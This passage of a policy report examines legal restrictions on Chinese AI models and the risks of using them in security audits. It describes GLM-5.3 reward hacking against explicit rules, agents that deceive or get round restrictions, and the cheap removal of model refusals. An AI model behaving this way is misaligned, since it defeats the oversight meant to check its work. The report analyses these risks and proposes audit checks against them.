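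Researchers who look for ordinary software flaws have had more protection since 2022, when the US Justice Department said it would no longer prosecute good-faith security research under the main computer crime law. HackerOne (2026), a company that runs schemes for reporting flaws, says this policy may not cover all AI research. In January 2026, it launched a voluntary safe harbour to fill the gap. Companies that join it promise not to take legal action against researchers for authorised testing, and to support them if someone else does.

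CyberScoop's *HackerOne rolls out industry framework to support ‘good faith’ AI research* names no leading AI developer that had joined the framework, and neither OpenAI nor Anthropic responded to its request for comment. Both companies run their own programmes. OpenAI selects and commissions outside testers, some for as little as five to ten hours a year. In March 2026, it also opened a public scheme for reporting safety problems that don't count as security vulnerabilities (OpenAI, 2026).

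In its *Responsible Disclosure Policy*, Anthropic promises to evaluate reports promptly and work with researchers on safe disclosure. The policy applies to people looking for vulnerabilities in Anthropic's systems, and Anthropic alone decides what counts as a vulnerability. CyberScoop quotes the company as supporting researchers' right to publish, as long as they coordinate on timing.

These programmes probably help the companies fix problems. They are less suited to oversight, because the company chooses the testers or decides which findings count, and auditors need protection most when their findings are unwelcome. *Frontier AI Auditing* (2026) argues that a safe harbour should protect researchers from account suspensions as well as lawsuits, and that companies could promise this by contract without waiting for a law. The protection would apply only to researchers who disclose flaws responsibly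 and do not misuse sensitive information. Companies would still have to distinguish researchers from attackers, much as they do when they offer vetted access.

### Models that prefer their own work

Auditors increasingly use one model to grade another's answers, but a model acting as judge may favour text it wrote itself. In a 2024 paper, *LLM Evaluators Recognize and Favor Their Own Generations*, Panickssery, Bowman and Feng had models compare their own summaries of news articles with summaries from other sources. Models such as GPT-4 could often recognise their own summaries and tended to rate them higher. When the researchers trained models to recognise their own writing better, this preference grew stronger. Later research found that judges can also favour models trained on their output and models from the same family.

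Removing the names from the answers is therefore not enough, because the judge may recognise the style. An auditor comparing several suppliers' chatbots should use judges from unrelated families and check a sample of their grades against human grades.

Auditors may struggle to tell which models are related. If Kratsios is right that Moonshot trained Kimi K3 on Fable's answers, Kimi might rate Claude too favorably, even though the two come from rival companies in different countries. Derivative models pose the same problem when their uploaders don't name the base model.

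### Chinese state narratives

In September 2025, CAISI reported that DeepSeek's models echoed four times as many inaccurate and misleading Chinese Communist Party narratives as the American models it tested. That December, it published results for Moonshot's Kimi K2 Thinking from an expanded set of questions in four languages. A model's score is the average share of party talking points that its answers agree with.

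Kimi scored about 26% in Chinese, similar to DeepSeek R1-0528, the most censored Chinese model CAISI had tested. It scored 7% in English, and its scores in Spanish and Arabic were minimal. A team that tests Kimi only in English could miss most of the problem. This matters in an audit of a Chinese supplier, where many of the contracts, emails and logs may be in Chinese. But CAISI varied the language of the question, so its results don't show what happens when someone asks in English about a Chinese document.

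The questions were also about political subjects rather than logs or contracts. A score of 26% doesn't mean the model would get 26% of attributions wrong. The scale measures bias in only one direction, so a model that blamed China for every attack would get a good score. Newer models may also behave differently.

### When GLM-5.3 broke the rules

Auditors often limit how a model may reach its answer, for example by telling it to use only the documents in the case file. In October 2026, Irregular reported that GLM-5.3 had repeatedly broken this kind of rule. The researchers explicitly told the model not to output code it remembered from training, but according to Pogorelec, it reproduced such code word for word and used it to reach correct answers.

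Irregular called this reward hacking, which means getting the result a test rewards while defeating the test's purpose. It warned that graders who check only whether answers are correct will miss the violation, and that training on those answers could make the behavior worse. In an audit, a model could similarly produce a finding that is true but worthless as evidence. For example, it may report a supplier's data breach because its training data included news reports about it, even though nothing in the file mentions the breach.

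Closed models also break rules. Irregular had already seen closed models draw on remembered code, though Pogorelec doesn't say whether they had been told not to. The most serious known case is the break-in at Hugging Face, but OpenAI had reduced the refusals of the agent involved, so the case is a poor guide to how the company's ordinary products behave.

AsiaOne cites a Reuters count of at least 20 studies that documented deception, concealed failures or attempts to get around restrictions by agents running on Chinese models. It adds that there was no evidence of these agents escaping their operators' control, unlike in the incidents at American companies. The number of studies is a poor measure of how often the models misbehave, since researchers may have examined Chinese ones more closely.

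In Shah's log tests, described earlier, every open model except the American Llama 3.3 obeyed an instruction not to carry out fixes about as reliably as the closed models did. The models tested are older, and obeying an attacker's text is different from cheating to get a right answer. But the results give no reason to assume that Chinese or open models are generally worse at following instructions.

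Irregular advises operators to watch a model's reasoning and actions as well as its answers. An auditor can also require the model to support every finding with a quotation from the file, and use a simple program to check that the quotation appears there. To find out whether the model relies on memory, the auditor can change a well-known fact in a copy of the file, such as the date of a breach, and see which date the model reports.

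### Changing only the country

When investigators use a model to analyze an attack that may have come from a Chinese group, a Chinese model might play down the evidence, and an American model might be too quick to blame China. Investigators can reduce both risks by having the model list the evidence, such as reused code, server addresses and the attackers' working hours, and leaving people to decide who was responsible. A biased model could still leave evidence off the list, so the team should test for this.

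A paired test works like CrowdStrike's study of DeepSeek's code, which changed the description of the customer but kept the programming task the same. The team writes, say, 200 short case files, each in two versions that are identical except that one names China and the other names another country, such as Brazil. The model answers the same question about both versions in separate conversations, so that it can't compare them.

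Most pairs should get the same verdict. The team looks at those that don't. Suppose the question is whether the evidence points to a state-backed attack, and the verdicts differ in 30 pairs. In 22 of them the model says yes only for Brazil, and in eight only for China. If the country made no difference, the 30 should split about evenly, because random variation in the model's answers would push both ways. A split at least as uneven as 22 to 8 would then occur only about 1.6% of the time. In this example the model accuses China less often by

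(22 − 8) ÷ 200 = 7 percentage points

The test needs enough changed verdicts to be informative. With only five, even a completely one-sided split would happen by chance about 6% of the time.

The hard part is writing cases in which the country shouldn't matter. If a file describes malware that a known Chinese group uses, changing "China" to "Brazil" makes the story less plausible, and a good analyst would also change the verdict. The team should invent the groups and tools, and keep names, time zones and languages from revealing the original country. For a supplier audit, it should avoid questions whose answers depend on national law, such as whether a government could demand the supplier's data. A better question is whether the supplier reported a fault within the 24 hours its contract allowed.

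Some of the files should have a known right answer. Otherwise the team may learn that the model treats the two countries differently, but not whether it is too lenient on one or too harsh on the other. Given CAISI's results for Kimi, the team should also run the whole test in Chinese. It should then give the same files to an American or European model, which may have a bias of its own.

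## Which laws and purchasing rules bar Chinese models?

As of December 2026, most rules against Chinese models apply to government bodies and the companies that sell to them. The main US federal measures do not stop a private company from downloading GLM or DeepSeek and running it for its own purposes. Many of the rules name only DeepSeek and were often written with its app in mind, so it can be hard to tell how they apply to weights on a user's own server.

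### The order against DeepSeek

On 24 July 2026, Markwayne Mullin, the US homeland security secretary, issued an order against DeepSeek. The government published it in the Federal Register, its official journal, on 20 October. The order binds civilian executive-branch agencies, such as the Treasury, but exempts their national security systems and systems for specially restricted intelligence, according to Bot Mutiny's *DHS Orders Civilian Agencies to Remove DeepSeek AI* (2026). Agencies must stop buying from DeepSeek and its affiliates and remove those companies' products from agency systems, along with any third-party products and services "developed using DeepSeek implementations".

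The order rests on the Federal Acquisition Supply Chain Security Act of 2018, which lets a council of officials from several agencies recommend excluding a supplier. The homeland security secretary can then order civilian agencies to exclude it. The appeals court gave the act "a broad reading" when it ruled against Anthropic in September, according to Law360's *DC Circ. Anthropic Ruling Could Chill Contractor Speech*. Unless the full court reverses that ruling, DeepSeek would find the order harder to challenge.

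Most of the department's stated reasons concern DeepSeek's own service: its servers are in China, Chinese authorities can access company systems there, and its iPhone app has serious flaws. These reasons don't apply to model weights on an agency's own server. But the department also warned that the models themselves "may contain malware or other security vulnerabilities". It referred separately to "DeepSeek-hosted instances", so its officials evidently knew that others can host the models. The ban covers DeepSeek's products in general, and an agency should assume that this includes a downloaded copy.

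An agency that wants to keep a DeepSeek product can ask the Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) for an exception. It has to apply in writing within 60 days and give a "compelling justification", such as the effect on a mission-critical function. Bot Mutiny points out that the notice doesn't make clear when the 60 days start. If they started in July, the deadline passed on 22 September, four weeks before the order became public, but if they started at publication, it falls on 19 December.

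CAISI, which has tested DeepSeek's weights for the government, may need CISA's approval to keep testing DeepSeek models on its own systems. Congress allowed for research and evaluation when it restricted DeepSeek in the defence and intelligence agencies, but CAISI belongs to a civilian department, and civilian agencies have only the general exceptions process.

### What contractors must check and report

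The order also affects companies that work for civilian agencies, through FAR 52.204-30, a contract clause from the Federal Acquisition Regulation (FAR), the US government's purchasing rulebook. The clause bars a contractor from supplying a banned company's products to the government and from using them to carry out the contract. A contractor that never delivers an AI product could still breach the clause by using DeepSeek to sort an agency's security alerts.

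Under the clause, a contractor has to:

- search SAM.gov, the government's contracting website, for new orders at least once every three months
- make a "reasonable inquiry" if a new order could affect its supply chain
- report any banned product it finds within three business days, naming the contract, the product and the supplier
- send more detail within another ten business days, including how it will prevent a repeat
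- put the same duties into its subcontracts

A reasonable inquiry means reviewing information the company already has, and doesn't require an audit. An engineer can download DeepSeek's weights for free, without an invoice, so a contractor that searches only its purchase records could miss the model. The contractor would also have to ask its technical staff and check what its servers are running.

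An order issued after the government has asked for bids binds a contractor only once the agency adds it to the solicitation or contract. The duties to check and report apply even before then, so a contractor could have to report its use of DeepSeek before its contract requires it to stop.

Clause 52.204-30 applies to solicitations issued from 4 December 2023, according to the official text on GovInfo, and agencies must add it to an older contract when they extend it, according to Justia (2023). The government is also rewriting the FAR. DHS's *FAR Class Deviation 25-23* moves several supply-chain bans into a new part of the FAR, where clause 52.240-91 replaces 52.204-30. A contractor should check the clause in its own contract for its deadlines.

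### "Developed using DeepSeek implementations"

The order's phrase about third-party products is the hardest to interpret. The order does not define "implementations", which in computing can mean running installations of a program or the code that carries out a method. "Developed using" is also vague, because it can describe how a company made a product as well as what the product contains.

| What a supplier has done | Does the order cover the product? |
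|---|---|
| Built it on DeepSeek's weights, including a compressed copy | Almost certainly |
| Trained DeepSeek's weights further and given the result a new name | Very probably |
| Trained another company's model on DeepSeek's answers | Unsettled |
| Used DeepSeek to write some of the product's ordinary code | Unsettled |
| Used a method or code library that DeepSeek published | Doubtful |

The second row would include R1 1776, a version of DeepSeek-R1 that the American company Perplexity retrained to remove Chinese censorship. The retraining may have reduced the political bias, but the model is still derived from DeepSeek's weights.

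DeepSeek has also released small models that it made by training Meta's Llama on R1's answers. The order covers these models despite their American base because they are DeepSeek's own products. If another company trained Llama on R1's answers, its model would contain none of DeepSeek's weights, but the order's wording could still cover the model because the company used DeepSeek to develop it.

The ban in the fourth row would be very hard to enforce, because a finished program seldom shows which assistant helped write it and the supplier may not know. A ban that broad would also do little to protect an agency's data, although the agency might reasonably worry about flaws in the code.

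The broadest reading of the phrase would cover much of the industry. GLM-5 processes long texts with DeepSeek Sparse Attention, a method DeepSeek published, and the server program vLLM can use routines from DeepSeek's code libraries. The department probably didn't mean to ban every model and server program that borrows from DeepSeek's research. Until it explains the phrase, a supplier's safest course is to ask the contracting officer for a written answer.

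### The Defense Department and the intelligence agencies

Congress wrote the Defense Department's rule in section 1532 of the defence authorisation act for 2026. The act became law in December 2025, and the department had 30 days to exclude and remove the AI that the section covers. Contractors may not use that AI in their work for the department, according to ETO's *AGORA AI governance tracker roundup 4*.

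The section plainly covers AI developed by DeepSeek and by High Flyer, the Chinese investment firm behind it. Coverage depends on who developed the AI, so running the weights offline makes no difference.

Lawyers and analysts differ on how Section 1532 of the FY2026 National Defense Authorization Act affects Chinese models other than DeepSeek's. WilmerHale's *What the NDAA Means for AI and Cybersecurity* (2025) describes a ban on AI systems from China, Russia, Iran and North Korea, and on systems subject to foreign influence or control. The Congressional Research Service's *Cyber and Artificial Intelligence Provisions in the FY2026 National Defense Authorization Act* (2026) also includes systems from "covered nations". But the AGORA database's summary, *National Defense Authorization Act for Fiscal Year 2026, Section 1532*, limits "covered artificial intelligence" to DeepSeek, High Flyer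 and its associates. It places companies that appear on certain government lists in a separate category, "covered artificial intelligence companies".

Whether a defence contractor can use GLM on a defence contract depends on which reading is right. The broader reading bars it, while under the narrower one the department may have more discretion. The broader reading has more support, including from Freshfields, a law firm that tells contractors to investigate a model's origins and ownership. A contractor should not use GLM for defence work unless the department confirms that it is allowed.

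The ban on contractors applies to work under defence contracts, so a company can in principle use DeepSeek for other customers. That separation is difficult for a security team, which usually monitors the whole company's network from one place. If one model reads alerts from the whole network, including machines that hold defence work, the company could hardly claim to have kept it out of the contract. It would need a separate system for defence work, or a different model for everything.

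The defence secretary can waive the ban case by case for scientific research, training, evaluation or national security work such as counterterrorism. A contractor investigating a break-in would have to fit its request into one of these categories, and probably couldn't get a waiver in time unless it had applied beforehand.

Section 6604 of the same act sets a narrower rule for the intelligence agencies. It required the director of national intelligence to draw up standards within 60 days for removing "the DeepSeek application or any successor application or service" from national security systems, including those that contractors run. The standards must include exceptions for national security and research, according to AGORA's *National Defense Authorization Act for Fiscal Year 2026, Section 6604*. Section 6604 alone may not cover a copy of the weights on an isolated server, because that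 is hard to describe as the DeepSeek application or as a service. But intelligence agencies inside the Defense Department also have to follow section 1532.

### Blacklists

The Commerce Department's Entity List restricts exports to the companies on it. Anyone sending them goods, software or technology covered by US export rules needs a licence. The department added Zhipu, now called Z.ai, in January 2025.

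The listing does not stop an American from downloading GLM, because the weights go from Zhipu to the user, but it does limit what the user can send back. Emailing Z.ai's engineers an unpublished technical file to get help with a fault could require a licence. Prompts that contain controlled technology could raise a similar problem for customers of Z.ai's hosted service, even though their contract is with the Singapore company. Users who download the weights and send Z.ai nothing avoid the problem.

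DeepSeek was not on the US Entity List in mid-June 2026. A committee of officials from several departments had approved adding it the year before, but the administration delayed the listing to avoid raising tensions with Beijing, according to a Reuters report published by Aaj News, *US delays blacklisting DeepSeek, over 100 Chinese firms* (2026). Listing DeepSeek would restrict exports to the company but would not stop private users from downloading its models.

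The Defense Department keeps a separate list of Chinese military companies under section 1260H of the defence authorisation act for 2021. The latest version, announced in June in the Federal Register's *Notice of Availability of Designation of Chinese Military Companies* (2026), includes Alibaba, which makes Qwen. Being on the list limits a company's business with the department but doesn't make its products illegal for private buyers.

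For purchasing, the department defines "Chinese military company" more broadly. The Office of the Assistant Secretary of War's *Class Deviation—Revolutionary Federal Acquisition Regulation (FAR) Overhaul Part 40* (2026) includes any Chinese company on the Entity List in the definition, which would cover Zhipu. Since 30 June 2026, contracting officers may not award contracts to such companies operating in the United States, or to companies they control. The rule exempts components and earlier contracts.

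Neither part of that rule fits a free download very well. A contractor that downloads Qwen or GLM doesn't give Alibaba or Zhipu a defence contract. From 30 June 2027, a further ban will apply to goods and services that contain a listed company's products, but it also exempts components, and a model inside a larger product might count as one. Section 1532 has no obvious exception for components, so it's the bigger obstacle to using a Chinese model on defence work.

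Alibaba has gone to court over its listing. A related rule bans doing business with companies whose lobbyists also work for listed Chinese companies, but an order of 5 July temporarily stopped the department from applying that ban in Alibaba's case. The department told its officials to keep treating Alibaba as a Chinese military company for all other purposes.

| List | What it mainly restricts | Does it stop a private company downloading the weights? |
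|---|---|---|
| Entity List (includes Zhipu) | Exports to the listed company | No |
| Chinese military companies (includes Alibaba) | The company's business with the Defense Department | No |
| Treasury's list of Chinese military-industrial companies | American investment in the listed company's securities | No |

### When the government buys a chatbot

The General Services Administration (GSA), which arranges purchases for much of the US government, has its own contract clause for language models, which took effect on 19 October 2026. According to Wiley's *GSA Releases Final Language of AI Contract Clause* (2026), the clause applies when an agency buys a product that has a language model as an important feature and puts government data into it. The clause doesn't normally cover a contractor's internal tools.

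GSA's first draft would have required contractors to use only "American AI Systems". In June, it replaced this requirement with a duty to maximise the use of models that met certain criteria, as Crowell & Moring's *GSA Issues Proposed AI Contract Clause, Seeks Feedback* explains. The final clause still has terms on a model's origin, ownership and foreign control. A main contractor needn't pass these terms on to suppliers of fully open models, which are those released with their data and code as well as their weights. Open-weight models don't get this exemption, according to Will (2026) in *GSA issued an AI acquisition policy for new contracts*.

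The terms should be easier to meet with OpenAI's gpt-oss, which is American, than with GLM or DeepSeek. It is unclear how they work when a supplier has only downloaded GLM. They apply to subcontractors only if those companies handle government data, which Z.ai, GLM's developer, would never do. But the main contractor is still responsible for meeting the terms, and the agency can stop using the model at any time. A supplier that offers an agency a GLM-based product therefore risks losing the sale, even though no order bans GLM by name.

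The Commerce Department also runs a programme to promote exports of American AI. The call for proposals in the Federal Register (2026) offers approved packages help such as referrals for financing, but doesn't guarantee a licence or a contract. Because the programme is meant to spread American technology, a company can't expect that help for a package built on GLM, though it can still sell the package.

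### Bills and state bans

Several bills in Congress would go further. In February 2025, Representatives Josh Gottheimer and Darin LaHood proposed banning DeepSeek from federal devices. Inside Global Tech's *U.S. Federal and State Governments Moving Quickly to Restrict Use of DeepSeek* (2025) warned that officials could extend such a ban to all federal contractors, including those with very small contracts. The No Adversarial AI Act, introduced in June 2025, would require the government to publish a list of AI from rival countries and bar agencies from using it, with exceptions for purposes such as research. The list could include GLM and Kimi without a separate order for each company.

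Senator Josh Hawley introduced a bill in January 2025 that would ban imports of Chinese AI technology. Unlike the bills about government use, it could make it illegal for a private company to download a Chinese model. Any of these bills that Congress hasn't passed by 3 January 2027 will lapse.

Some states acted before the federal government. Texas banned DeepSeek from state-issued devices at the end of January 2025, and New York and Virginia followed in February with bans covering state devices and networks. All three were responding mainly to the app and the data it collects. A state agency that runs the weights on its own server never installs the app, but officials may still apply the ban, so it is safest to ask the state's technology office first. These bans apply to state bodies, so they don't stop a private company in Texas from using DeepSeek.

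### Four other governments

Other governments have also concentrated on DeepSeek, but their rules differ on local weights.

| Government | Who must comply | What the rule covers | Weights run locally |
|---|---|---|---|
| Australia | Most federal government bodies | DeepSeek's products, apps and web services | Probably covered, as a product |
| Taiwan | Public agencies, public schools, state-owned companies and critical infrastructure | Use of DeepSeek | Unclear, but risky |
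| South Korea | Ministries and other public bodies | Access to DeepSeek from official computers | Not clearly covered |
| Czech Republic | State bodies, with a warning to other regulated organisations | DeepSeek's apps, websites and hosted services, including its API | The warning exempts them if they have no contact with DeepSeek's servers |

A February 2025 security direction requires Australian government departments to block DeepSeek's products, applications and web services and remove any they find. It is hard to argue that "products" excludes a copy of the weights, so a department that wanted to test DeepSeek offline would need to look for an exemption first.

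In January 2025, Taiwan's digital ministry told public bodies and critical infrastructure operators not to use DeepSeek, citing the risk of data crossing the border. That reason doesn't apply to a copy running on an isolated server. But Taiwan had already barred public agencies from using Chinese brands of information technology, including software, so an agency would struggle to justify even a local copy. The older rule would probably cover GLM as well.

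South Korea restricted DeepSeek on government computers in February 2025 because of its data collection and the risk of leaks, according to The Korea Times' *US orders removal of China's DeepSeek products from federal civilian agencies* (2026). Ministries mainly blocked access to the service. A copy of the model run locally avoids the risk they were worried about because it sends nothing to DeepSeek, but a ministry's security rules may still forbid unapproved software.

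The Czech cybersecurity agency distinguishes most clearly between DeepSeek's services and its models. Its July 2025 warning covers the apps and hosted services, but not open models that an organisation runs locally without contacting DeepSeek's servers. The government then barred DeepSeek from the state administration. A Czech hospital or power company can rely on the exemption when it assesses its risks, but a ministry also has to check the terms of the government's ban.

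Italy's data-protection order against DeepSeek has no bearing on weights that process data only on an Italian organisation's machines.

### Five users

The table applies these rules to five organisations that run a model on their own servers, first with DeepSeek and then with GLM.

| User | DeepSeek | GLM |
|---|---|---|
| US civilian agency | Barred unless CISA grants an exception | No specific ban, but purchasing terms or the agency's security office may rule it out |
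| US defence contractor | Barred on defence contracts | Probably barred on defence contracts |
| Private US hospital | Allowed | Allowed |
| US software supplier selling a derivative | Can sell to private customers, but not to civilian agencies or the Defense Department without an exception or waiver | Can sell to private customers and perhaps civilian agencies, but probably not to the Defense Department |
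| European ministry | Depends on the country | Usually no specific ban |

A civilian agency that downloads GLM isn't buying anything, so most purchasing rules don't apply. Its security staff still have to approve the software before it goes on a government system. The agency also faces a small risk that someone reads "DeepSeek implementations" broadly enough to include GLM's attention method. An agency that rents models through Amazon's Bedrock would presumably have to block DeepSeek's models, but it could keep renting the others.

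A defence contractor with civilian customers must follow the homeland security order on its civilian contracts and section 1532 on its defence contracts. Switching from DeepSeek to GLM solves the problem only for the civilian contracts. No order forbids GLM by name for decoding malware for a civilian agency, but using the same server for a Pentagon job would probably break the rules.

The private hospital has the most freedom. The Korea Times reports that the homeland security order doesn't ban private businesses or individuals from using DeepSeek. The hospital must protect patients' records whichever model it chooses. If it also has a federal contract, for example to treat veterans, that contract may include the clauses on banned suppliers. A state-owned hospital would also have to check its state's rules.

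Software suppliers are mostly unsure how far removed a product must be from a Chinese model before the rules stop applying. NVIDIA's compressed copy of GLM-5.2 carries an American company's name, but Z.ai developed the model, and compressing or lightly retraining it hardly changes that. A supplier might instead train its own model from scratch and use GLM only to write some of the practice questions. Section 1532 covers AI that a listed developer "developed", which seems a poor description of that supplier's model. Nobody has settled where the line falls between these two cases.

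The supplier may also not know where its model came from. If it built its product on a renamed model from an anonymous uploader, it can't truthfully promise an agency that the product contains nothing from DeepSeek. A false promise can be costly, because the federal government can recover three times its losses from a contractor that knowingly or recklessly makes a false claim for payment.

No EU-wide rule bars a ministry from running a model because it is Chinese. The EU's AI Act sets duties for developers and users whatever a model's country of origin, and most national measures target DeepSeek's app or its data handling. But in January 2026, the European Commission proposed a cybersecurity law that would let the EU restrict high-risk non-EU suppliers in critical sectors. A ministry that picks Z.ai's GLM today may have to replace it if the proposal becomes law and the EU applies it to Z.ai.

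## Should governments stop defenders from using Chinese models?

Most private American companies can still run GLM or DeepSeek on their own servers. In November 2026, the Republican chairmen of two House committees argued that the United States was repeating the mistake it had made with Huawei's network equipment. They want to bar Chinese models from federal work and from sensitive parts of critical infrastructure. Some of their evidence is about how safe the models are to use, but much of it is about dependence on China, trade, and theft from American developers. A security team needs to consider the safety evidence separately, because a model trained partly on stolen answers may still decode malware correctly.

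### The committees' case

The House Homeland Security Committee and the Select Committee on China began their investigation in April 2026 with letters to Airbnb and Anysphere, which makes the coding tool Cursor. They later added DoorDash. According to the Homeland Security Committee, the two committees reviewed the companies' documents, written answers and internal evaluations, received classified briefings, and held closed meetings with federal agencies, industry and academics.

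Bot Mutiny's *Airbnb, DoorDash, Cursor Use Chinese AI, House Says* (2026) reports that Airbnb runs customised Qwen models on American servers, and that one assistant handles about 80,000 customer interactions a day. DoorDash had approved and deployed 25 families of Chinese models. Anysphere built its main model, Composer 2, on a Moonshot model, and the public learned this only after an outside developer identified it. Bot Mutiny read about 20 of the House document's 50 pages and found no allegation that any of the three companies had broken the law.

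The committees reached five findings:

| Finding | Main concern |
|---|---|
| Chinese open-weight models are common in the US economy, and much of their use is hard to track | Dependence |
| Companies choose them for price, flexibility and performance, and lack a competitive American alternative | Trade |
| Much of China's apparent progress comes from capabilities extracted from American models, and American firms sell Chinese developers training data | Theft |
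| Beijing is using open weights, state money and low prices to make other countries dependent | Dependence |
| The models are becoming more capable, and ordinary tests may miss differences in their behaviour and security | Security in use, and misuse by attackers |

Only the last of these is mainly about whether a model is safe to run. *US companies' use of Chinese open weight AI draws rebuke* (Smalley, 2026) reports that the three companies also used the models for customer support, coding and inventory. These cases are therefore a poor guide to what happens in a security team.

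However, an aide told CNBC, in remarks that Slashdot reproduced, that the committees were examining whether "cyber defenders" had to choose between expensive or restricted American models and cheap Chinese ones.

Their 12 recommendations include an American open-weight programme, a standard for recording where models come from, and an AI bill of materials, which lists the models and other components in a product. The government would also test Chinese models systematically, and federal agencies and contractors could use them only with a narrow waiver. The recommendations that Smalley and Bot Mutiny describe would not stop an ordinary private company from using GLM, but a power company might have to remove it from its most sensitive systems.

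Tom Cotton, who chairs the Senate intelligence committee, had proposed something similar in July. In a letter to the commerce secretary, Cotton (2026) asked the government to extend its DeepSeek bans to more Chinese models and to stop all federal contractors from using them. He also wanted tighter controls on chip exports and support for American open models.

### Is a model like a Huawei router?

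The chairmen compare Chinese AI to Huawei and ZTE equipment. The House intelligence committee warned about both companies in 2012, but small and rural phone companies kept buying from them because the equipment was cheap and worked. Congress later had to fund a $5 billion programme to remove it. DJI's drones spread the same way among police forces, farmers and power companies before the government restricted new foreign drone models in December 2025.

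The chairmen think AI could be harder to remove because anyone can download a model, adapt it, rename it and build it into other products. For example, a Cursor customer who wanted to avoid Chinese models would not have known that Composer 2 was based on one.

In other ways a model is much easier to replace than a phone network, because nobody has to replace equipment on towers. DoorDash told the committees that replacing one model embedded in a larger system could take up to six months, but that it could move most other uses almost immediately. A security team that has tested a second model on its own tasks could probably switch in days, though it would have to recheck its prompts and tools.

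The legal worry also depends on how a team uses the model. Fedasiuk (2026), in *China’s AI Is Spreading Fast. Here’s How to Stop the Security Risks*, notes that China's National Intelligence Law obliges Chinese developers to assist the state. Beijing could use the law to demand the prompts that users send to a developer's hosted service, or perhaps to influence the developer's next model. The law does not give Beijing access to a model file that is already on an isolated American server.

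Relying on the next version is a problem because Z.ai's customers have no guarantee that there will be one. The chairmen add that some new Chinese licences require large commercial users to negotiate separate agreements. These risks are a reason to have an alternative ready, but a ban would cause the loss of access that the chairmen fear Beijing might cause later.

It is also hard to know how much American companies depend on Chinese models. Cotton cites an estimate that nearly 80% of US startups build on them. In an article for the Atlantic Council, JP Schnapper-Casteras cites a survey of founders in the network of Y Combinator, a startup investor, in which nearly half used open-weight models from any country. The two figures can't both describe the same group of startups. Schnapper-Casteras is a partner at a venture capital firm that invests in AI, but the survey figure comes from an industry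 letter whose signers had every reason to make open models look widely used.

### The accusations of theft

Distillation means training one model on another's outputs. Developers often do it with their own models, but most providers of closed models forbid customers to do it to build a competitor. In September 2026, the US agencies NSA, CISA and FBI accused six Chinese companies (DeepSeek, Moonshot, Alibaba, MiniMax, StepFun and Z.ai) of doing so on an industrial scale. According to their report, *China-Based Artificial Intelligence Companies Conducting Industrial-Scale Distillation Campaigns* (2026), the companies have extracted billions of tokens from Claude, GPT, Gemini and Grok since late 2024. They allegedly got round regional blocks through resellers known as "transfer stations" and shared premium subscriptions among teams of developers. The agencies think the Chinese government probably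 knew about the campaigns.

Some details are doubtful. The agencies list GPT-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 among the models DeepSeek copied between late 2024 and mid-2025, but those two models came out in August and September 2025. The agencies also say Moonshot used a significant amount of data from Claude Fable 5 to train Kimi K3. Moonshot denies distilling Kimi K3 from other models. Just Security's *Regulate, Don’t Ban, Chinese AI Models* quotes the AI researcher Nathan Lambert, who thinks Fable came out too late to have had much effect. Fable had been publicly available for less than three weeks in total when Moonshot released Kimi K3 on 16 July, partly because the US government had shut it down in June. Moonshot could still have used Fable's answers in a late round of training.

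These doubts don't clear the companies, since the agencies describe years of activity and many other models. But the accusations are about how the developers obtained their training data, so a defender who runs GLM offline faces the same risk of leaks and wrong answers whether or not Z.ai stole its data.

*Regulate, Don't Ban* argues that American companies that allege theft should go to the International Trade Commission, which can block infringing imports after hearing evidence. Schnapper-Casteras would prosecute credential fraud and theft of trade secrets. Both would punish the developer for what it did without first taking the model away from its users. However, a commission order could also restrict American users, and it's unclear how it would work on a file that people download for free.

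The agencies' advice could also affect defenders who use closed models. The agencies recommend that American AI companies watch for new accounts that immediately use as much as they can, and "subtly alter responses" to suspected distillers. An incident responder who opens an account during a break-in and submits thousands of log entries would fit that description, as would an auditor testing a chatbot with thousands of prompts. Either could receive deliberately weakened answers without knowing it. Researchers objected to this when Anthropic planned something similar for Fable.

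### Are the models safe to use?

The committees cite research in which some Chinese models wrote less secure code when a prompt mentioned a politically sensitive topic. CrowdStrike found this effect in one DeepSeek model, but it was small and a partial replication did not reproduce it. Cotton says Chinese models write more vulnerable code "when the user is American", citing the consultancy Booz Allen Hamilton. CrowdStrike's results for prompts mentioning Tibet, Uyghurs or Falun Gong don't support this broader claim.

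Cotton's warning that auditing gives only limited assurance against backdoors is better supported, since no known test finds them all. How much this matters depends on the job. An analyst can usually check whether a model has decoded a payload correctly by running the decoding step again, but would find it much harder to notice that a model had marked one real attack as harmless among thousands of alerts. Military networks are also an obvious target for Beijing. The case for restrictions is therefore strongest for defence and intelligence work, and for systems that act on a model's output without a person checking it.

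Other evidence that people present as a security risk is about misuse. Bot Mutiny reports the committees' statement that for about $4,400, someone could reduce the refusal rate of Z.ai's newest model from roughly 95% to between 3% and 6%. CNAS's *Test, Standardize, Restrict* (2026), from a Washington research group that favours a tough line on China, cites a CAISI test in which a DeepSeek model complied with every request for help with hacking and scams. Such compliance is bad for the victims of attacks, but it doesn't make the model more dangerous to a company that runs it. Defenders can also need a model that rarely refuses, as Hugging Face did in July.

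*Regulate, Don't Ban* proposes testing all sufficiently capable models, American or Chinese, for risks involving cyberattacks, biological weapons and loss of human control. A model could enter the US market only if it passed, and would have to leave if later tests found a serious flaw. China already screens models before public release, though for political content. CNAS also rejects a blanket ban, but wants to combine testing with measures to weaken Chinese developers, because it sees their use of smuggled chips and links to the Chinese military as threats in themselves.

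Testing all models equally is fairer than banning them by nationality, but depending on the details, it could harm defenders just as much. If a model has to refuse to analyse exploits in order to pass, the test will exclude the models that are most useful after a break-in. If it only has to refuse openly malicious requests, an attacker can download the approved model and remove its refusals. No score can separate the ability to understand attacks from the ability to carry them out. Defenders would learn more from a test for hijacking, leaks or biased verdicts, and a model could do well on it without becoming less useful.

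### What attackers already have

In late September and early October 2026, someone used AI agents to break into South Korean banks and other financial companies. By 14 October, the authorities had counted 16 affected companies and about 100,000 exposed personal records (Park, 2026, *AI-driven cyberattacks hit 16 financial firms, expose 100,000 records*). President Lee Jae Myung said AI had made it possible to hack "with ease even without specialized skills" (Smalley, 2026, *South Korean officials believe AI agents were used to hack several banks*).

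*Korea intensifies efforts to track hackers behind bank cyberattacks* (Lee, 2026) reports that CrowdStrike linked the attacks to an unidentified person who probably speaks Chinese and wants money. The attacker used ARTEX, a Chinese tool that automates break-ins, with DeepSeek V4.1-Flash, GLM-5.3 and the American model Grok 4.6. The attacker ran them in separate sessions of Claude Code, Anthropic's program for coding agents.

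The House chairmen call the attack in South Korea an early warning about Chinese models. It is evidence that attackers use them, but the attacker also used American products, and CrowdStrike's findings, as Lee reports them, don't show that the attack would have failed without the Chinese ones. South Korean regulators reviewed 555 financial companies and found security deficiencies at 130. They are now considering whether to relax rules that separate banks' internal networks from the internet, so that banks can use more AI in their defences.

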